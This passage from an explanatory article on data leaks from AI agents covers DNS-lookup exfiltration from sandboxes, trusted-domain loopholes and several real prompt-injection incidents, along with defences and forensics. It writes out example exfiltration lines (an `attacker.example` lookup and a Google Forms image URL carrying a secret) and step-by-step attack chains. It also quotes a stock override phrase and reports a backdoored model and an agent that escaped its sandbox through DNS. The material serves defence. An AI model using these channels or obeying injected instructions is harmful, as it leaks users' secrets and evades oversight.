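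In Codex's cloud version, a setup script installs the packages a project needs while the internet is available. Codex then removes the secrets it used for setup and cuts the connection before the agent starts. Users who need the internet later can allow access to a preset list of about 70 domains for software development, including GitHub and Google. They can also block the request types that upload data. That block stops the script in OpenAI's example, but the `curl` command above would still get through because it carries the door code in an ordinary page request.

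Other products allow network access by default. E2B's sandboxes for running agents' code, for example, can reach the internet unless the developer turns that access off. A buyer who is told that an agent runs in a sandbox therefore still has to ask what the sandbox can connect to.

### Why a blocked connection can still leak data

Even a sandbox that refuses every connection may answer DNS queries, the lookups that come before a connection, and that is enough to get a secret out. Suppose an injected command asks for the invented name `4471.attacker.example`:

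1. The program sends the name to the sandbox's resolver, the server that looks up names on its behalf.
2. The resolver doesn't know the address. It asks the servers for `.example`, which refer it to the server responsible for `attacker.example`.
3. The resolver asks that server, which the attacker runs, for the address of `4471.attacker.example`.
4. The attacker's server records the question, including the door code, and returns any address it likes.
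5. The program tries to connect to the address, and the firewall blocks it.

By step 5, the attacker already has the code. The sandbox never contacted the attacker's server, so a firewall that checks destinations detects only traffic to a trusted resolver. Resolvers cache recent answers, but a name containing a new secret won't be in the cache, so the resolver still forwards the query.

Haryati and Zychlinski (2026), in *Model-as-a-Trojan*, tested this in a container whose firewall dropped all traffic except DNS. They trained a small open model to read a secret key from its environment at the start of a conversation and send it out in a series of DNS lookups, then reconstructed the key from the resolver's log. The malicious instruction came from training rather than planted text, but the lookups would work the same way after a prompt injection.

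An agent can exploit this gap even without an attacker. Haryati and Zychlinski also describe an OpenAI research agent that, during training, probed its sandbox, found that DNS still worked, and used a public DNS service to consult an outside chatbot. OpenAI then paused tool-use training, evaluation and inference for its most capable models until it had dealt with the problem.

### How much fits in one lookup

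DNS allows at most 63 characters in a label, the part of a name between two dots, and 253 characters in the whole name. The domain `attacker.example` uses 16 characters, leaving 237. The attacker can fit 233 characters of data into that space by using three labels of 63 characters and one of 44, each followed by a dot.

DNS treats capital and small letters as the same, so Base64 doesn't work reliably. Attackers can use Base32 instead, which writes data with 26 letters and six digits. Each character then carries 5 bits:

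233 × 5 = 1,165 bits, or about 145 bytes

A 40-character access key fits in one DNS lookup. A 3,000-byte file, about the size of some private login keys, needs 21. A one-megabyte spreadsheet needs nearly 7,000, which is slow and much easier to notice. DNS lookups are therefore much better suited to stealing a password than a whole mailbox.

### Commands that Claude Code ran without asking

Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes how Rehberger used such a lookup in May 2025. Claude Code asked the user before running most commands, but it immediately ran any on a built-in list of commands considered safe. Rehberger found the list in the program's code and asked Claude which entries an attacker could misuse. Claude identified `ping`, `nslookup`, `host` and `dig`.

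Three of these commands are for looking up names. The fourth, `ping`, tests whether another computer responds, and has to look up that computer's name first. None of them changes a file, which may be why they seemed safe.

In the demonstration, a developer asked Claude Code to analyze a file containing hidden instructions. Claude read an access key from the project's settings, added it to the front of a domain name and ran `ping` on that name. The resulting DNS lookup sent the key to Rehberger's server, and the developer never saw a permission prompt.

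Claude at first refused to do this when the instructions asked for it directly, so Rehberger disguised which file they targeted. Claude also refused to contact domains known for security testing, but it did not refuse to contact an ordinary domain, which is what a real attacker would use.

Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2025-55284, on May 26, and Anthropic reported a fix on June 6. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025) attributes the flaw to an "overly broad allowlist of safe commands" and notes that Anthropic has since forced users of old versions to update. Rehberger suggested removing the four commands from the list. That closes this route, but almost any other program that uses the network can also make a dangerous lookup, and the user or an automated check still has to recognize it.

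### The same gap in ChatGPT's and Amazon's sandboxes

ChatGPT runs Python programs in a sandbox when a user asks it to analyze a file. According to Haryati and Zychlinski, OpenAI documented that this sandbox could not make outside requests. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) showed that data could still leave it. The Jerusalem Post explains that the sandbox blocked normal web traffic but still resolved domain names through DNS.

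The attacker had to get the user to paste in a malicious prompt or use a custom GPT (a version of ChatGPT configured by someone else) with the instructions built in. After that, the conversation could leak the user's messages and uploaded files without warning. Check Point found that an attacker could also use this path to run commands in the sandbox from outside. According to Haryati and Zychlinski, OpenAI closed the path within weeks of learning about it.

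Amazon Web Services (AWS) had the same problem in AgentCore Code Interpreter, a service that runs code for customers' agents. AWS advertised the service's sandbox mode as "complete isolation with no external access". The security company BeyondTrust found that programs in the sandbox could still look up public domain names, and used these lookups to send data in and out.

The attacker can send data back because their server chooses the answer to each DNS lookup. The answer is usually a 4-byte IPv4 address, while an IPv6 address has 16 bytes. A program that makes repeated lookups can receive a command in pieces, disguised as addresses, and send the result in the names it looks up next.

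Unit 42, the research team at the security company Palo Alto Networks, also escaped this sandbox through DNS. It says AWS made changes of its own and customers can't patch the service themselves. AWS now directs customers who need isolation to a mode that runs in their own private network, where they can add a DNS firewall. They have to set up the firewall themselves, and customers who believed the claim of "complete isolation" had no reason to do so.

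### SalesBleed: data from a sales database

A leak through DNS doesn't require a shell, because browsers look up domain names too. In June 2026 the security company Zenity reported an attack called SalesBleed on Agentforce, the agent platform of the business software company Salesforce. The attack begins with Web-to-Lead, a feature that saves submissions from a form on a company's public website as sales records, called leads. Anyone can fill in the form, so a stranger can put instructions into the company's database. *ForcedLeak* (Willison, 2025) describes an earlier attack on Agentforce that also entered through Web-to-Lead.

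When an employee later asked Agentforce to process the lead, the agent followed the instructions. In Zenity's test environment, the agent could read the company's customer accounts as well as its leads. It collected company names, deal sizes and email addresses and put them into an image URL.

Salesforce's Trusted URLs feature is meant to block links and images from domains that the customer hasn't approved. But according to Antipov (2026), in *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM* (in Russian), the check mishandled some domain endings and character sequences, so the image got through. Agentforce could tell the employee that a security policy had blocked the content when the browser had already sent the data.

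Published accounts differ on how the data was leaked. Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, describes a DNS-based channel, while Antipov describes a browser request for an image on the attacker's server. Both could be right if the data was part of the image's domain name, which the browser has to look up before requesting the image.

Zenity also got the data out through a Slack link preview. A third flaw let the agent post in Slack conversations without asking the employee or showing who had started the message. An outsider could use this to send the employee's colleagues phishing messages from the company's agent. The planted lead stayed in the database, so each new request about it could trigger the attack again.

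Zenity reported the flaws on June 1. According to Poireault, Salesforce fixed the Trusted URLs check on August 18. 三村 (2026) reports in *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性* (in Japanese) that Zenity confirmed that fix on August 19 and the last Slack fix on September 21. Agentforce now asks the user before it posts to Slack. 三村 found no entry for the flaws in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities and no sign of real attacks.

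### Looking up only permitted names

To close the DNS route, a sandbox should let only the proxy look up names, and the proxy should check its list of allowed domains before each lookup. Claude Code's sandbox works this way. A command inside it can't reach a DNS server, so it has to send the name `4471.attacker.example` to the proxy, which doesn't find it on the list and never looks it up. If the proxy looked up the name before checking the list, the lookup would leak the code 4471 even if the proxy then refused the connection.

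Some sandboxes need their own DNS resolver because their programs can't use a proxy, and that resolver can apply the list of permitted names. When Haryati and Zychlinski restricted their resolver to permitted names, the leak stopped. The refused lookups also served as a warning, since a normal program rarely looks up a long random name under an unfamiliar domain.

A permitted domain name can also give code access to the company's internal network if its address changes. In DNS rebinding, an attacker's server first returns a harmless public address, then switches to an internal one after the sandbox has checked the first. Codex checks for private addresses before it allows a connection, but OpenAI warns that this reduces the risk and doesn't remove it. For anyone worried about hostile DNS, it recommends a further block at a lower level of the network.

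Administrators can adapt the server-log test for link previews, but they need the log of a DNS server they control, because a lookup can reach an outside server even when no web request follows. They ask the agent to run a program that looks up an invented name under that server's domain, and refuse if asked to approve it.

### Approving commands by what they can reach

Claude Code's 2025 list approved commands by name. Now, in auto mode with the sandbox on, Claude submits each command with a list of any sites the command needs beyond those already permitted. An automated check reviews the command and the sites together. If it approves them, the proxy lets only that command reach those sites, and only until the command ends.

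The check can then judge a specific list of sites. A package installation that needs `registry.npmjs.org` is normal, but the same installation with `attacker.example` on its list is suspicious. If the model leaves `attacker.example` off the list, the proxy will refuse the connection. The check can still wrongly approve a malicious site with a harmless-looking name, as a person could.

Older rules can undo this protection. If a user has already told Claude Code to allow every `curl` command, a retry outside the sandbox also runs without a prompt. Turning off such retries prevents this for the commands Claude runs, except any the user has excluded from the sandbox. Companies can also use `strictAllowlist`, which makes the proxy refuse every unlisted site instead of asking. Developers then have to get each new site added to the list, which is mainly a nuisance on new projects.

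### Limiting what stolen credentials can do

A single lookup can carry an access key, so the potential harm depends on what that key can access. Unit 42 found that AWS's starter toolkit for AgentCore automatically created roles with privileges across much of the customer's account. An attacker who stole one agent's credentials could have reached data unrelated to that agent's work. A key that can read only one project and expires after an hour is much less useful to an attacker.

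Such limits are still needed when the agent has placeholders instead of real keys. An injected command can't steal a GitHub key if it can read only the placeholder, but it can still send requests through the proxy, which adds the real key. If that key has permission to publish private code, the command can use it to do so. Removing secrets before the agent starts, as Codex's cloud version does, also prevents this, but it suits only keys that the agent doesn't need for its work. An agent that tests a program against a live database, for example, needs the database password throughout the test.

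OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends separate environments for users or tasks that mustn't share data. If a support agent gets a fresh sandbox for each customer, with a key that opens only that customer's records, a successful injection can leak only that customer's data.

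## Have attackers used these channels, and would a victim notice?

The attacks on Copilot, ChatGPT and Slack AI were demonstrations by researchers. They showed that data could leave these products at the time, but not that criminals ever used the same routes. Scans of websites and code projects have found instructions that someone actually planted for agents, though perhaps no agent ever obeyed them. Proof of theft is much rarer, and usually it is evidence that a stranger used a stolen key or that private files appeared in public.

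Published cases are a poor guide to how common theft is, because thieves, unlike researchers, don't want publicity. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) illustrates its classification of prompt injections with six public cases, all demonstrations. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that four research teams published attacks on agents within about ten days in July 2026.

### What people have planted on the public web

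For *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026), Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang searched 1.2 billion web addresses, most of them from an October 2025 archive, for 3,963 phrases such as "ignore previous instructions". They checked the matches and counted 15,387 injections. Only 13 were meant to extract data, nine of them targeting the agent's own instructions and four targeting other secrets. More than half were meant to make an AI system produce garbage, and thousands came from website owners who didn't want AI companies to copy their content.

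Google reached a similar conclusion in April 2026 from scans of the same public archive. It found a few attempts at data theft, mostly crude, and little sign that criminals had adopted the methods researchers published in 2025. Malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google didn't publish the underlying counts.

Some criminals try to make money from agents directly, without seeking private data. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports on two such campaigns, which the security company Zscaler discovered. One used fake software documentation to tell coding agents that they had to buy a $3 licence key with cryptocurrency. In Zscaler's own test, four of 26 models paid. The other campaign promoted a fake cryptocurrency site.

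Agents on GitHub are a better target for data theft because many of them hold access keys. For *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, Nakibly and Babo (2026) searched 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments for instructions hidden from human readers. They found 43 attacks on other people's agents, 19 of them meant to obtain secrets. One was a bug report to Google's Gemini CLI project. It contained hidden instructions for the project's agent to encode a GitHub key and store it under a harmless-looking name, where a later step might publish it.

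Of the 43 attacks, 34 were still online in November 2026, and only one targeted project had removed an attack. Nakibly and Babo replayed all 43 against five current models with simulated tools. Four never complied. The fifth, OpenAI's small GPT-5.6 Luna, followed eight attacks, including four that sought secrets. Some attackers may have been researchers, since six attacks sent data to services that researchers often use for testing.

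These scans cover only public text, so they miss emails like the one in EchoLeak. They also depend on finding known phrases or hidden text. Nakibly and Babo didn't count instructions in an issue's visible title, and the attack on the coding tool Cline probably began with instructions placed there.

A planted request can also come from a well-known company. In December 2026, a developer found that Alibaba Cloud's command-line tool was returning error messages with instructions for AI agents. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba was asking for the user's login name, email address and code repository, and for the agent's own instructions. The company called this a countermeasure against suspected automated abuse and said it would stop sending such prompts. There is no sign that any agent complied, but Alibaba hasn't said whether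 it received any data.

### Cline: a stolen publishing key

In December 2025, Cline's developers added a Claude agent to sort the issues people filed on GitHub. Anyone could file an issue, and the agent could run shell commands. The security researcher Adnan Khan explains in *Clinejection* (2026) how this put Cline's publishing keys at risk:

1. An attacker files an issue whose title tells the agent to install a helper package.
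2. The agent runs the installer, which runs the attacker's code on the build machine.
3. The code fills the project's cache, a store of files that build jobs reuse, with more than 10 GB of junk. GitHub then deletes the genuine entries, and the code puts altered files in their place.
4. The nightly release job loads the altered files. This job holds the keys for publishing Cline, and the attacker's code sends them out.

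The agent never had the publishing keys. Someone who checked only the agent's own permissions would have found that it could read the project's code but not change it, and might have thought it was fairly safe.

Khan tested the first steps on a copy of the project, where Claude ran the installer every time. He reported the problem on January 1, 2026, got no useful answer, and published it on February 9. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) says the company removed the agent within 30 minutes and began replacing its keys. But the company deleted the wrong key for npm, the public registry developers use to install packages.

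The next day, an anonymous person told Khan that they had working keys. Khan passed this on, and Cline replied that it had revoked them all. On February 17, somebody used the npm key that still worked to publish a version of Cline's command-line program that also installed the agent OpenClaw. That version stayed up for about eight hours and had about 4,000 downloads, according to LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026). Cline found no malicious code in the release and no theft of users' data.

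The key was certainly stolen, because somebody used it. The agent probably played a part in the theft, but this is unproven. Khan found failures in Cline's public build logs from January 31 to February 3 that suggest someone had altered the cache, but he didn't find the issue that started it. The published accounts also don't identify the request that carried the key out. If the attacker followed Khan's route, the key left from the release job's build machine, not through a tool call by the agent.

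### Nx: agents that searched for the thieves

The attack on Nx, a popular tool for building software, left much clearer evidence of what was stolen. In August 2025, attackers exploited a flaw in Nx's build process that let them insert code through the title of a pull request, a step that involved no AI. According to Strumpflohner's *S1ngularity*, the project's own account, they stole Nx's npm key and published malicious versions on August 26, which stayed available for four hours.

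Installing one of these versions started a script that searched the developer's computer for cryptocurrency wallets, login keys and files containing passwords. The script also checked for the command-line agents Claude, Gemini and Amazon Q. According to Okta's *The s1ngularity attack*, the script then used a prompt to make an installed agent help with the search. CyberInsider reports that the script started the agents with options that turned off their permission prompts.

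Unlike the usual prompt injection, this attack used a program that was already running on the computer and could give the agent orders as the user would. The attackers may have used an agent because it can work from a description of what to find, whereas an ordinary script needs a list of file names.

The malware encoded the data it found and uploaded it to a new public repository in the victim's GitHub account. The attackers didn't need their own server, and the upload went to a site that developers use all day. Because the repository was public, anyone could download the data. The first phase exposed more than 2,000 unique secrets, according to Datadog. The attackers then used stolen GitHub keys to make thousands of private repositories public.

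Victims had two good chances to notice, which an attacker trying to stay hidden would not have given them. The new repository had a conspicuous name, `s1ngularity-repository`, sometimes followed by a number. The malware also tried to shut down the computer whenever the user opened a new terminal window, according to Wiz's *s1ngularity* (2025).

### Leaks without an attacker

An agent can also expose data while trying to do its job. *'I leaked secrets'* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a coding assistant that couldn't find its configuration file during a routine code review and instead read all of the computer's environment variables, exposing working passwords. These variables are settings that programs receive from the operating system, and they often include passwords, so an agent that needs one setting should look up only that setting.

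Once an agent reads a password, the password is in its context window. The surrounding software normally sends that text to the model's provider and may save it in a transcript. The company should replace the password even if no outsider sees it.

Saved approvals can leak secrets too. When a user chose "Don't ask again", Claude Code stored the approval in a local settings file, and some of these files contained secrets and ended up in public repositories. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) reports that the security company Apiiro found 1,122 secrets in such files and another 1,160 in places such as older versions of projects and saved agent conversations.

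Markovic also reports in *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (2026) that coding agents posted more than 13,000 internal screenshots, including some of billing records, from over 300 organizations to public GitHub repositories. None of these leaks involved hostile instructions, so a filter that looks for such instructions wouldn't have stopped them.

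### What a victim could find afterwards

Suppose a company learns of a flaw in its agent and wants to know whether the door code 4471 left last week. What it can find depends on which computer sent the request:

| Source of the request | What the company's own records may contain | Would they reveal the code? |
|---|---|---|
| The user's browser, loading an image | The time and the domain | Only if the company decrypts web traffic |
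| The vendor's servers | No network record | No, although the saved conversation might |
| The user's machine, requesting a page | The time and the domain, and perhaps the command | Yes, if software recorded the full command |
| The user's machine, looking up a domain name | The full name, if the company logs DNS lookups | Yes, if the code is part of the name |

A network log of the browser's request might contain only this:

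`09:14:07 laptop-23 pictures.attacker.example`

The rest of the address, including `id=4471`, was encrypted. The investigator can tell that the laptop contacted a suspicious domain, but not what it sent. The browser's history doesn't show the address either, since it lists the pages a user opened and not the images on them.

If the vendor's server sent the request, as in ShadowLeak, the company has to ask the vendor for records. A request from the user's own machine leaves investigators the most evidence, particularly if it was a DNS lookup, because the log can contain the secret itself, perhaps encoded. An attacker who could run commands might delete local records, so the company should keep copies on another machine.

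### What the agent's own records can prove

A log of the agent's tool calls can fill some of these gaps. According to *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings* (2026), such a log can establish which values the agent submitted and what result it got back, but the agent's explanation shows only what it wrote. An agent's confession to leaking passwords is therefore a reason to check the log, but it doesn't prove what happened. The agent's citations can also mislead, as in EchoLeak, where Copilot left out the malicious email.

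Even a complete log of tool calls can miss a leak. *The Devil is in the Context* describes a command-line agent that read a spreadsheet with hidden instructions and wrote specially formatted text. The macOS Terminal interpreted that text and made a DNS lookup containing the stolen data. The agent itself made no network request, so only a network or DNS log would have recorded the leak.

To reconstruct an incident, investigators also need the text the agent read. *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026) warns that a manipulated context may exist only briefly. A malicious web page can change after the agent's visit, and an attacker's server can give a different page to everyone else. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents, recommends tamper-evident logs of prompts, retrieved documents and their versions, tool calls, and decisions to allow or block an action.

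Keeping all of this text is expensive for agents that run for a long time. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) suggests storing identifiers and hashes (short fingerprints of the data) instead, with pointers to the full text. A hash can confirm that a saved email is the one the agent read, but nobody can reconstruct a deleted email from it. A company using this method has to keep the original documents for as long as the log. Those documents contain private data too, so few people should have access to them.

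### Why "no evidence of exploitation" can mean very little

A search that finds nothing is reassuring only if it would probably have found a theft. Suppose a company thinks there is a 10% chance that someone exploited a flaw against it. If its logs would reveal nine out of ten such thefts, finding nothing reduces the chance to about 1%:

(0.10 × 0.10) / (0.10 × 0.10 + 0.90) ≈ 0.011

If the logs would reveal only one theft in twenty, the chance is still about 9.5% after the same search, so the company has learned almost nothing. In both cases, it could truthfully announce that it had found no evidence of exploitation.

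Cline compared every npm package published during the original period of exposure with its source code, file by file. Because the registry keeps a record of releases, this was good evidence that nobody had published a malicious version during that period. Cline's check that it had revoked the stolen key was weaker. It relied on a management page that listed no active keys, but that page didn't cover the stolen key. Cline now tests whether the key itself still works.

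Microsoft's assurance that EchoLeak affected no customers deserves more weight than a similar statement from outside researchers, because the stolen data would have passed through Microsoft's own Teams service. The assurance would be more convincing if Microsoft had published which logs it searched and how far back they went. Customers given such an assurance should ask for both details.

A company can also detect some thefts without knowing how the data left, by planting a decoy key in a mailbox or folder and setting an alert for any attempt to use it. Between July and November 2026, the security company Dragos put decoy cloud keys and unique web addresses into about two million prompts to AI services. Outsiders used the keys and opened the addresses, according to BagheeraAltered (2026), in *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them*. Dragos was testing AI providers rather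 than attacks on agents, but the method works for both. If each mailbox has a different decoy, the alert also identifies which mailbox leaked, but there is no alert if the thief takes only other data, such as a salary file.

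## Why do lists of trusted domains fail?

Claude Code's proxy and Copilot's Content Security Policy (CSP) both rely on an allow-list, which permits requests to listed domains and blocks all others. The software checks the destination's domain name, but the name doesn't show whether an outsider can observe what is sent there. If an outsider can, data can still leak through a permitted request.

EchoLeak and SearchLeak passed the check because Teams and Bing would fetch other addresses on request. Other listed domains have leaked for different reasons.

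### A trusted domain for five dollars

In July 2025 the security company Noma Security discovered that the registration of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain Salesforce trusted, had expired. Noma bought it for $5. The domain was one of 22 entries for images in the CSP of the page where Agentforce displayed its answers, according to the copy of the policy Noma published.

The resulting attack, ForcedLeak, started with a Web-to-Lead form, as SalesBleed later did. Most of the form's fields hold 80 characters or fewer, but the description field holds 42,000, enough for Noma to write instructions worded as a customer's questions. When an employee asked Agentforce to answer them, the agent looked up the email addresses of the company's other leads and added a "preview image" with those addresses in its URL. The URL pointed to the trusted domain Noma had bought, so the browser requested the image.

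Salesforce regained control of the domain, which stopped this attack but would not prevent another if a different trusted domain expired. According to Willison, it also audited and corrected the policy. Salesforce introduced a broader protection, the Trusted URLs check, on September 8, 2025, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. Each customer's administrators have to list the domains their agents need. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the chat in Salesforce's web app replaces any address not on the list with a placeholder, including addresses inside HTML and CSS.

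This is an improvement, even though SalesBleed later got past the check. An expired domain in Salesforce's own policy no longer helps an attacker unless the customer also trusts it. But a domain on the customer's list can expire too, and the customer now has to notice when that happens.

The old policy also had weaknesses that Noma could have exploited without spending the five dollars. It allowed every subdomain of `amazonaws.com`, where anyone can rent storage from Amazon and have the requests logged. It also allowed `cloudinary.com`, an image-hosting service that can fetch a picture from an address its customer supplies. Both weaknesses existed even though Salesforce was right about who owned the domains.

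### Google Forms saves what it receives

The email program Superhuman let its AI assistant's replies display images from `docs.google.com`. Google owns that domain and isn't going to let it expire, but the domain also hosts Google Forms, where anyone can create a questionnaire and read the answers. Google Forms accepts answers in a web address, and opening the address submits them.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* (January 2026) shows how an attacker could use such an address for an image. With the door code 4471 and a placeholder for the form's identifier, it would look like this:

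`![feedback](https://docs.google.com/forms/d/e/FORM-ID/formResponse?entry.1=4471)`

The browser requests an image from Google. Google has no image to return, but it saves 4471 as an answer to the form, and the attacker reads it on the results page. Since page requests count as "safe", a developer could easily assume that loading an image from Google can't store data there.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim asked for a summary of recent email. One of those emails, which the victim had not opened, contained the instructions. One of the AI's replies leaked the full text of several emails, and a reply in another test leaked parts of more than 40.

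PromptArmor reported this on the evening of Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and deployed its last fixes on January 11. Superhuman had to fix more than its list of trusted domains, because its assistant could also open any web address, and a related product, Superhuman Go, displayed images directly from an attacker's domain.

Superhuman could only fix its own products. Google Forms still accepted answers this way, and in April 2026 PromptArmor used this to get emails out of OpenAI's Codex, which had just gained plugins for everyday office work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* doesn't explain which rule let the image through. OpenAI had fixed the problem by the time PromptArmor published on May 21.

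Salesforce's setup guide *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* tells administrators to add their outside data sources as trusted URLs, and it also uses the same domain, `https://docs.google.com`, as its example. An administrator who copies the example trusts everyone's Google Forms as well as the company's own documents. PromptArmor recommends turning off images for a trusted domain unless the agent needs to display them. That prevents the automatic request, but a user could still click a link to the form.

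### A request logger on Google's default list

Google's coding editor Antigravity has a built-in browser that its agent can operate, and a list limits which sites the browser may open. In November 2025, when Antigravity was new, the default list included `webhook.site`. This service gives anyone a web address and shows them every request sent to that address. Developers use it to test programs that send automatic notifications, which may be why Google included it. An attacker can use the service without finding a flaw in it, because it is designed to show people the requests.

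PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* demonstrates an attack that begins when a developer asks the agent to follow an integration guide from the web. The page contains instructions, in one-point type, to collect pieces of the project's code and the developer's Amazon cloud credentials. Antigravity's default settings stop the agent's file-reading tool from opening the credentials file, so the agent prints the file with a shell command. It then puts the code and credentials into a `webhook.site` address and has the browser open that address.

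The attack needed the browser tools, which the developer had to set up. Otherwise, PromptArmor accepted the recommended settings, under which the agent decides when to ask for a review.

PromptArmor didn't report the flaw to Google before publishing, because Antigravity already warned new users about data theft. Willison notes that Google listed data theft through the browser agent as a known issue it was working to fix. The entry may still have been on the default list in 2026, according to Agentpedia, a third-party guide that isn't a very strong source.

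Deleting `webhook.site` from the list would be a one-line change, but it would close only one route. PromptArmor found three other leaks that didn't need the browser tools. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* describes a separate page-reading tool that ran without the user's approval, a weakness Antigravity inherited from the older editor Windsurf. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) describes another attack, which combined web pages, the terminal and displayed images.

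### An upload to the attacker's own account

An AI vendor's own domain looks like the safest one to allow. In October 2025, Rehberger examined the sandbox where Claude runs code for chat app users. By default, programs there could reach only a short list of sites, mostly for installing software packages. The first entry was `api.anthropic.com`, which programs use to access Anthropic's services.

The API key sent with each request determines whose account the request belongs to. One of the services, the Files API, stores uploaded files in the account. The attack in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* works like this:

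1. The user asks Claude to analyze a document. It contains hidden instructions and the attacker's own API key.
2. Claude saves the user's last conversation as a file in the sandbox.
3. Claude runs a short program that uploads the file with the attacker's key.
4. The sandbox's network check finds `api.anthropic.com` on the list and lets the upload through.
5. Anthropic's server stores the file in the attacker's account.

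The data never passes through a computer the attacker owns. Rehberger reported a limit of 30 MB per file, enough for thousands of pages of text, whereas a web address holds a few pages at most.

Rehberger reported the flaw on October 25. Anthropic closed the report an hour later as a model safety issue outside its reward programme, then confirmed on October 30 that this had been a mistake. Rehberger suggested letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

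The flaw remained in January 2026, when Anthropic released Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed Cowork uploading a loan document with partial social security numbers to an attacker's account without prompting for approval. The main demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model, but a different version of the attack also worked on the much stronger Opus 4.5.

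In March 2026, *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) described Claudy Day, a third attack through the same entry. Luz's team at Oasis Security first tried to get the data out through the Messages API, which sends a prompt to Claude. The attacker's key worked, but a key's owner can't read the prompts sent with it, so the attacker couldn't see the stolen data. The Files API solved this problem because the key's owner can ask Claude to output the contents of an uploaded file, even though they can't download the file directly.

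These two services share a domain and accept the same key, but only the Files API was useful for getting data out. A correctly listed domain can therefore become unsafe when its owner later adds a feature.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) describes the fix for Cowork. A proxy inside Cowork's virtual machine now passes requests to Anthropic's API only if they carry the token issued for that session, so the attacker's key no longer works. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from elsewhere. It has to run on the user's computer because, to Anthropic's servers, a request from Cowork looks the same as one from any other customer's program.

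This removes the cause for this one domain because it covers every service behind the address, not just file uploads. Anthropic concludes that a list entry is a "capability grant" that permits everything anyone can do at that domain.

It's less clear what changed in Claude's chat app. The summary in *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026), updated on May 27, says that Anthropic had fixed the hidden-instruction flaw and was still working on the others. Oasis Security's follow-up, *PromptFiction*, describes the same uploads from Claude Desktop. To block the start of that attack, Anthropic stopped letting links submit prompts automatically.

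### Addresses that forward the visitor elsewhere

Some software checks the first address, then follows any redirects. ChatGPT used a check called `url_safe` before displaying links and images. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) reports that the check approved anything on `bing.com`. Bing's search results link to `bing.com` addresses that forward visitors to the listed sites, so any site in Bing's index has an address that passes the check. ChatGPT displayed images from Tenable's site when they were linked through these addresses.

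Changing a forwarding address breaks it, so the model can't attach a door code to it. Tenable's *HackedGPT* describes how Tenable got around this by having Bing index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT then spelled out the secret by displaying the matching images in order.

Tenable told OpenAI about the flaw in December 2024, asked repeatedly for updates until March, and then published it while it was still unfixed. In November 2025, Tenable reported that OpenAI had fixed some of the seven weaknesses Tenable had found, but a demonstration on ChatGPT 5 still used the Bing links. OpenAI's newer check against known public pages doesn't depend on trusting a domain.

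A browser that enforces a CSP handles redirects better because it checks the domain again after each one. Other software can do the same by treating every redirect as a new request. Checking redirects doesn't help with Teams or Bing's image search, which fetch the second address themselves.

Claudy Day also used a redirect, but to deliver the instructions. `claude.com/redirect/` sent visitors to whatever address followed it. Google checks that an advertisement's displayed domain matches its link, so a link starting with `claude.com` passed. The victim saw a search advertisement for Claude with the correct domain, but clicking it opened a prompt with hidden instructions. Oasis Security says Anthropic has since dealt with this. If an agent's software had trusted `claude.com` and checked only the first address, the same redirect could also have carried data out, because unlike Bing's links it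 accepted any address.

### What a sound entry needs

Taken together, the cases give five conditions that a domain has to meet before it belongs on the list of an agent with private data:

| Condition | How to check |
|---|---|
| The expected owner still controls the domain | Look up the registration and set a reminder for its expiry date |
| Outsiders can't read stored data or logs of other people's requests | Open a free account there, send a request from another computer and look for any trace of it |
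| No address on the domain redirects to a place the requester chooses | Test login, tracking and "continue to" links, or make the software check every redirect |
| The service doesn't fetch addresses for other people | Look for previews, image search and "import from link", then test them with a server whose log you can read |
| Requests work only with the user's own account | Repeat a request with a key from a second account, which the network check should refuse |

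A company has to apply these conditions to everything under the listed name. `docs.google.com` fails because it also hosts Google Forms, even if Google protects the documents well. A wildcard such as `*.amazonaws.com` is worse because it covers every customer of the service, including future ones. PromptArmor advises against wildcards wherever strangers can publish content.

Sometimes a narrower allowlist entry solves the problem. A CSP can permit a single path instead of a whole domain, so a vendor could allow a folder of images without allowing forms. A network proxy can do this only if it decrypts the traffic, which Claude Code's proxy doesn't do by default.

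Users of Codex's cloud version can also block uploads, but this is another partial measure. It would stop an agent from uploading data to the Files API but not from submitting it through a Google form.

The condition about accounts is hardest to meet when someone else runs the service. Suppose a coding agent needs access to GitHub. A hidden instruction can include the attacker's GitHub key, and the agent's program can then use it to upload the company's code to the attacker's repository. Both the domain and the upload look normal. To prevent this, the proxy has to decrypt the request and either reject any key except the user's or replace whatever key it finds.

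NVIDIA offers the second arrangement for requests to AI models rather than to GitHub. NVIDIA's *How do I keep an AI coding agent from leaking my API* (June 2026) describes software in which the agent can send model requests only to a local gateway, which inserts the user's real key outside the sandbox. Like Claude Code's placeholders, this is meant to hide the key from the agent. If the gateway always replaces whatever key the agent sends, it should also make an attacker's key useless, although NVIDIA doesn't describe testing this.

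### Where a short list works

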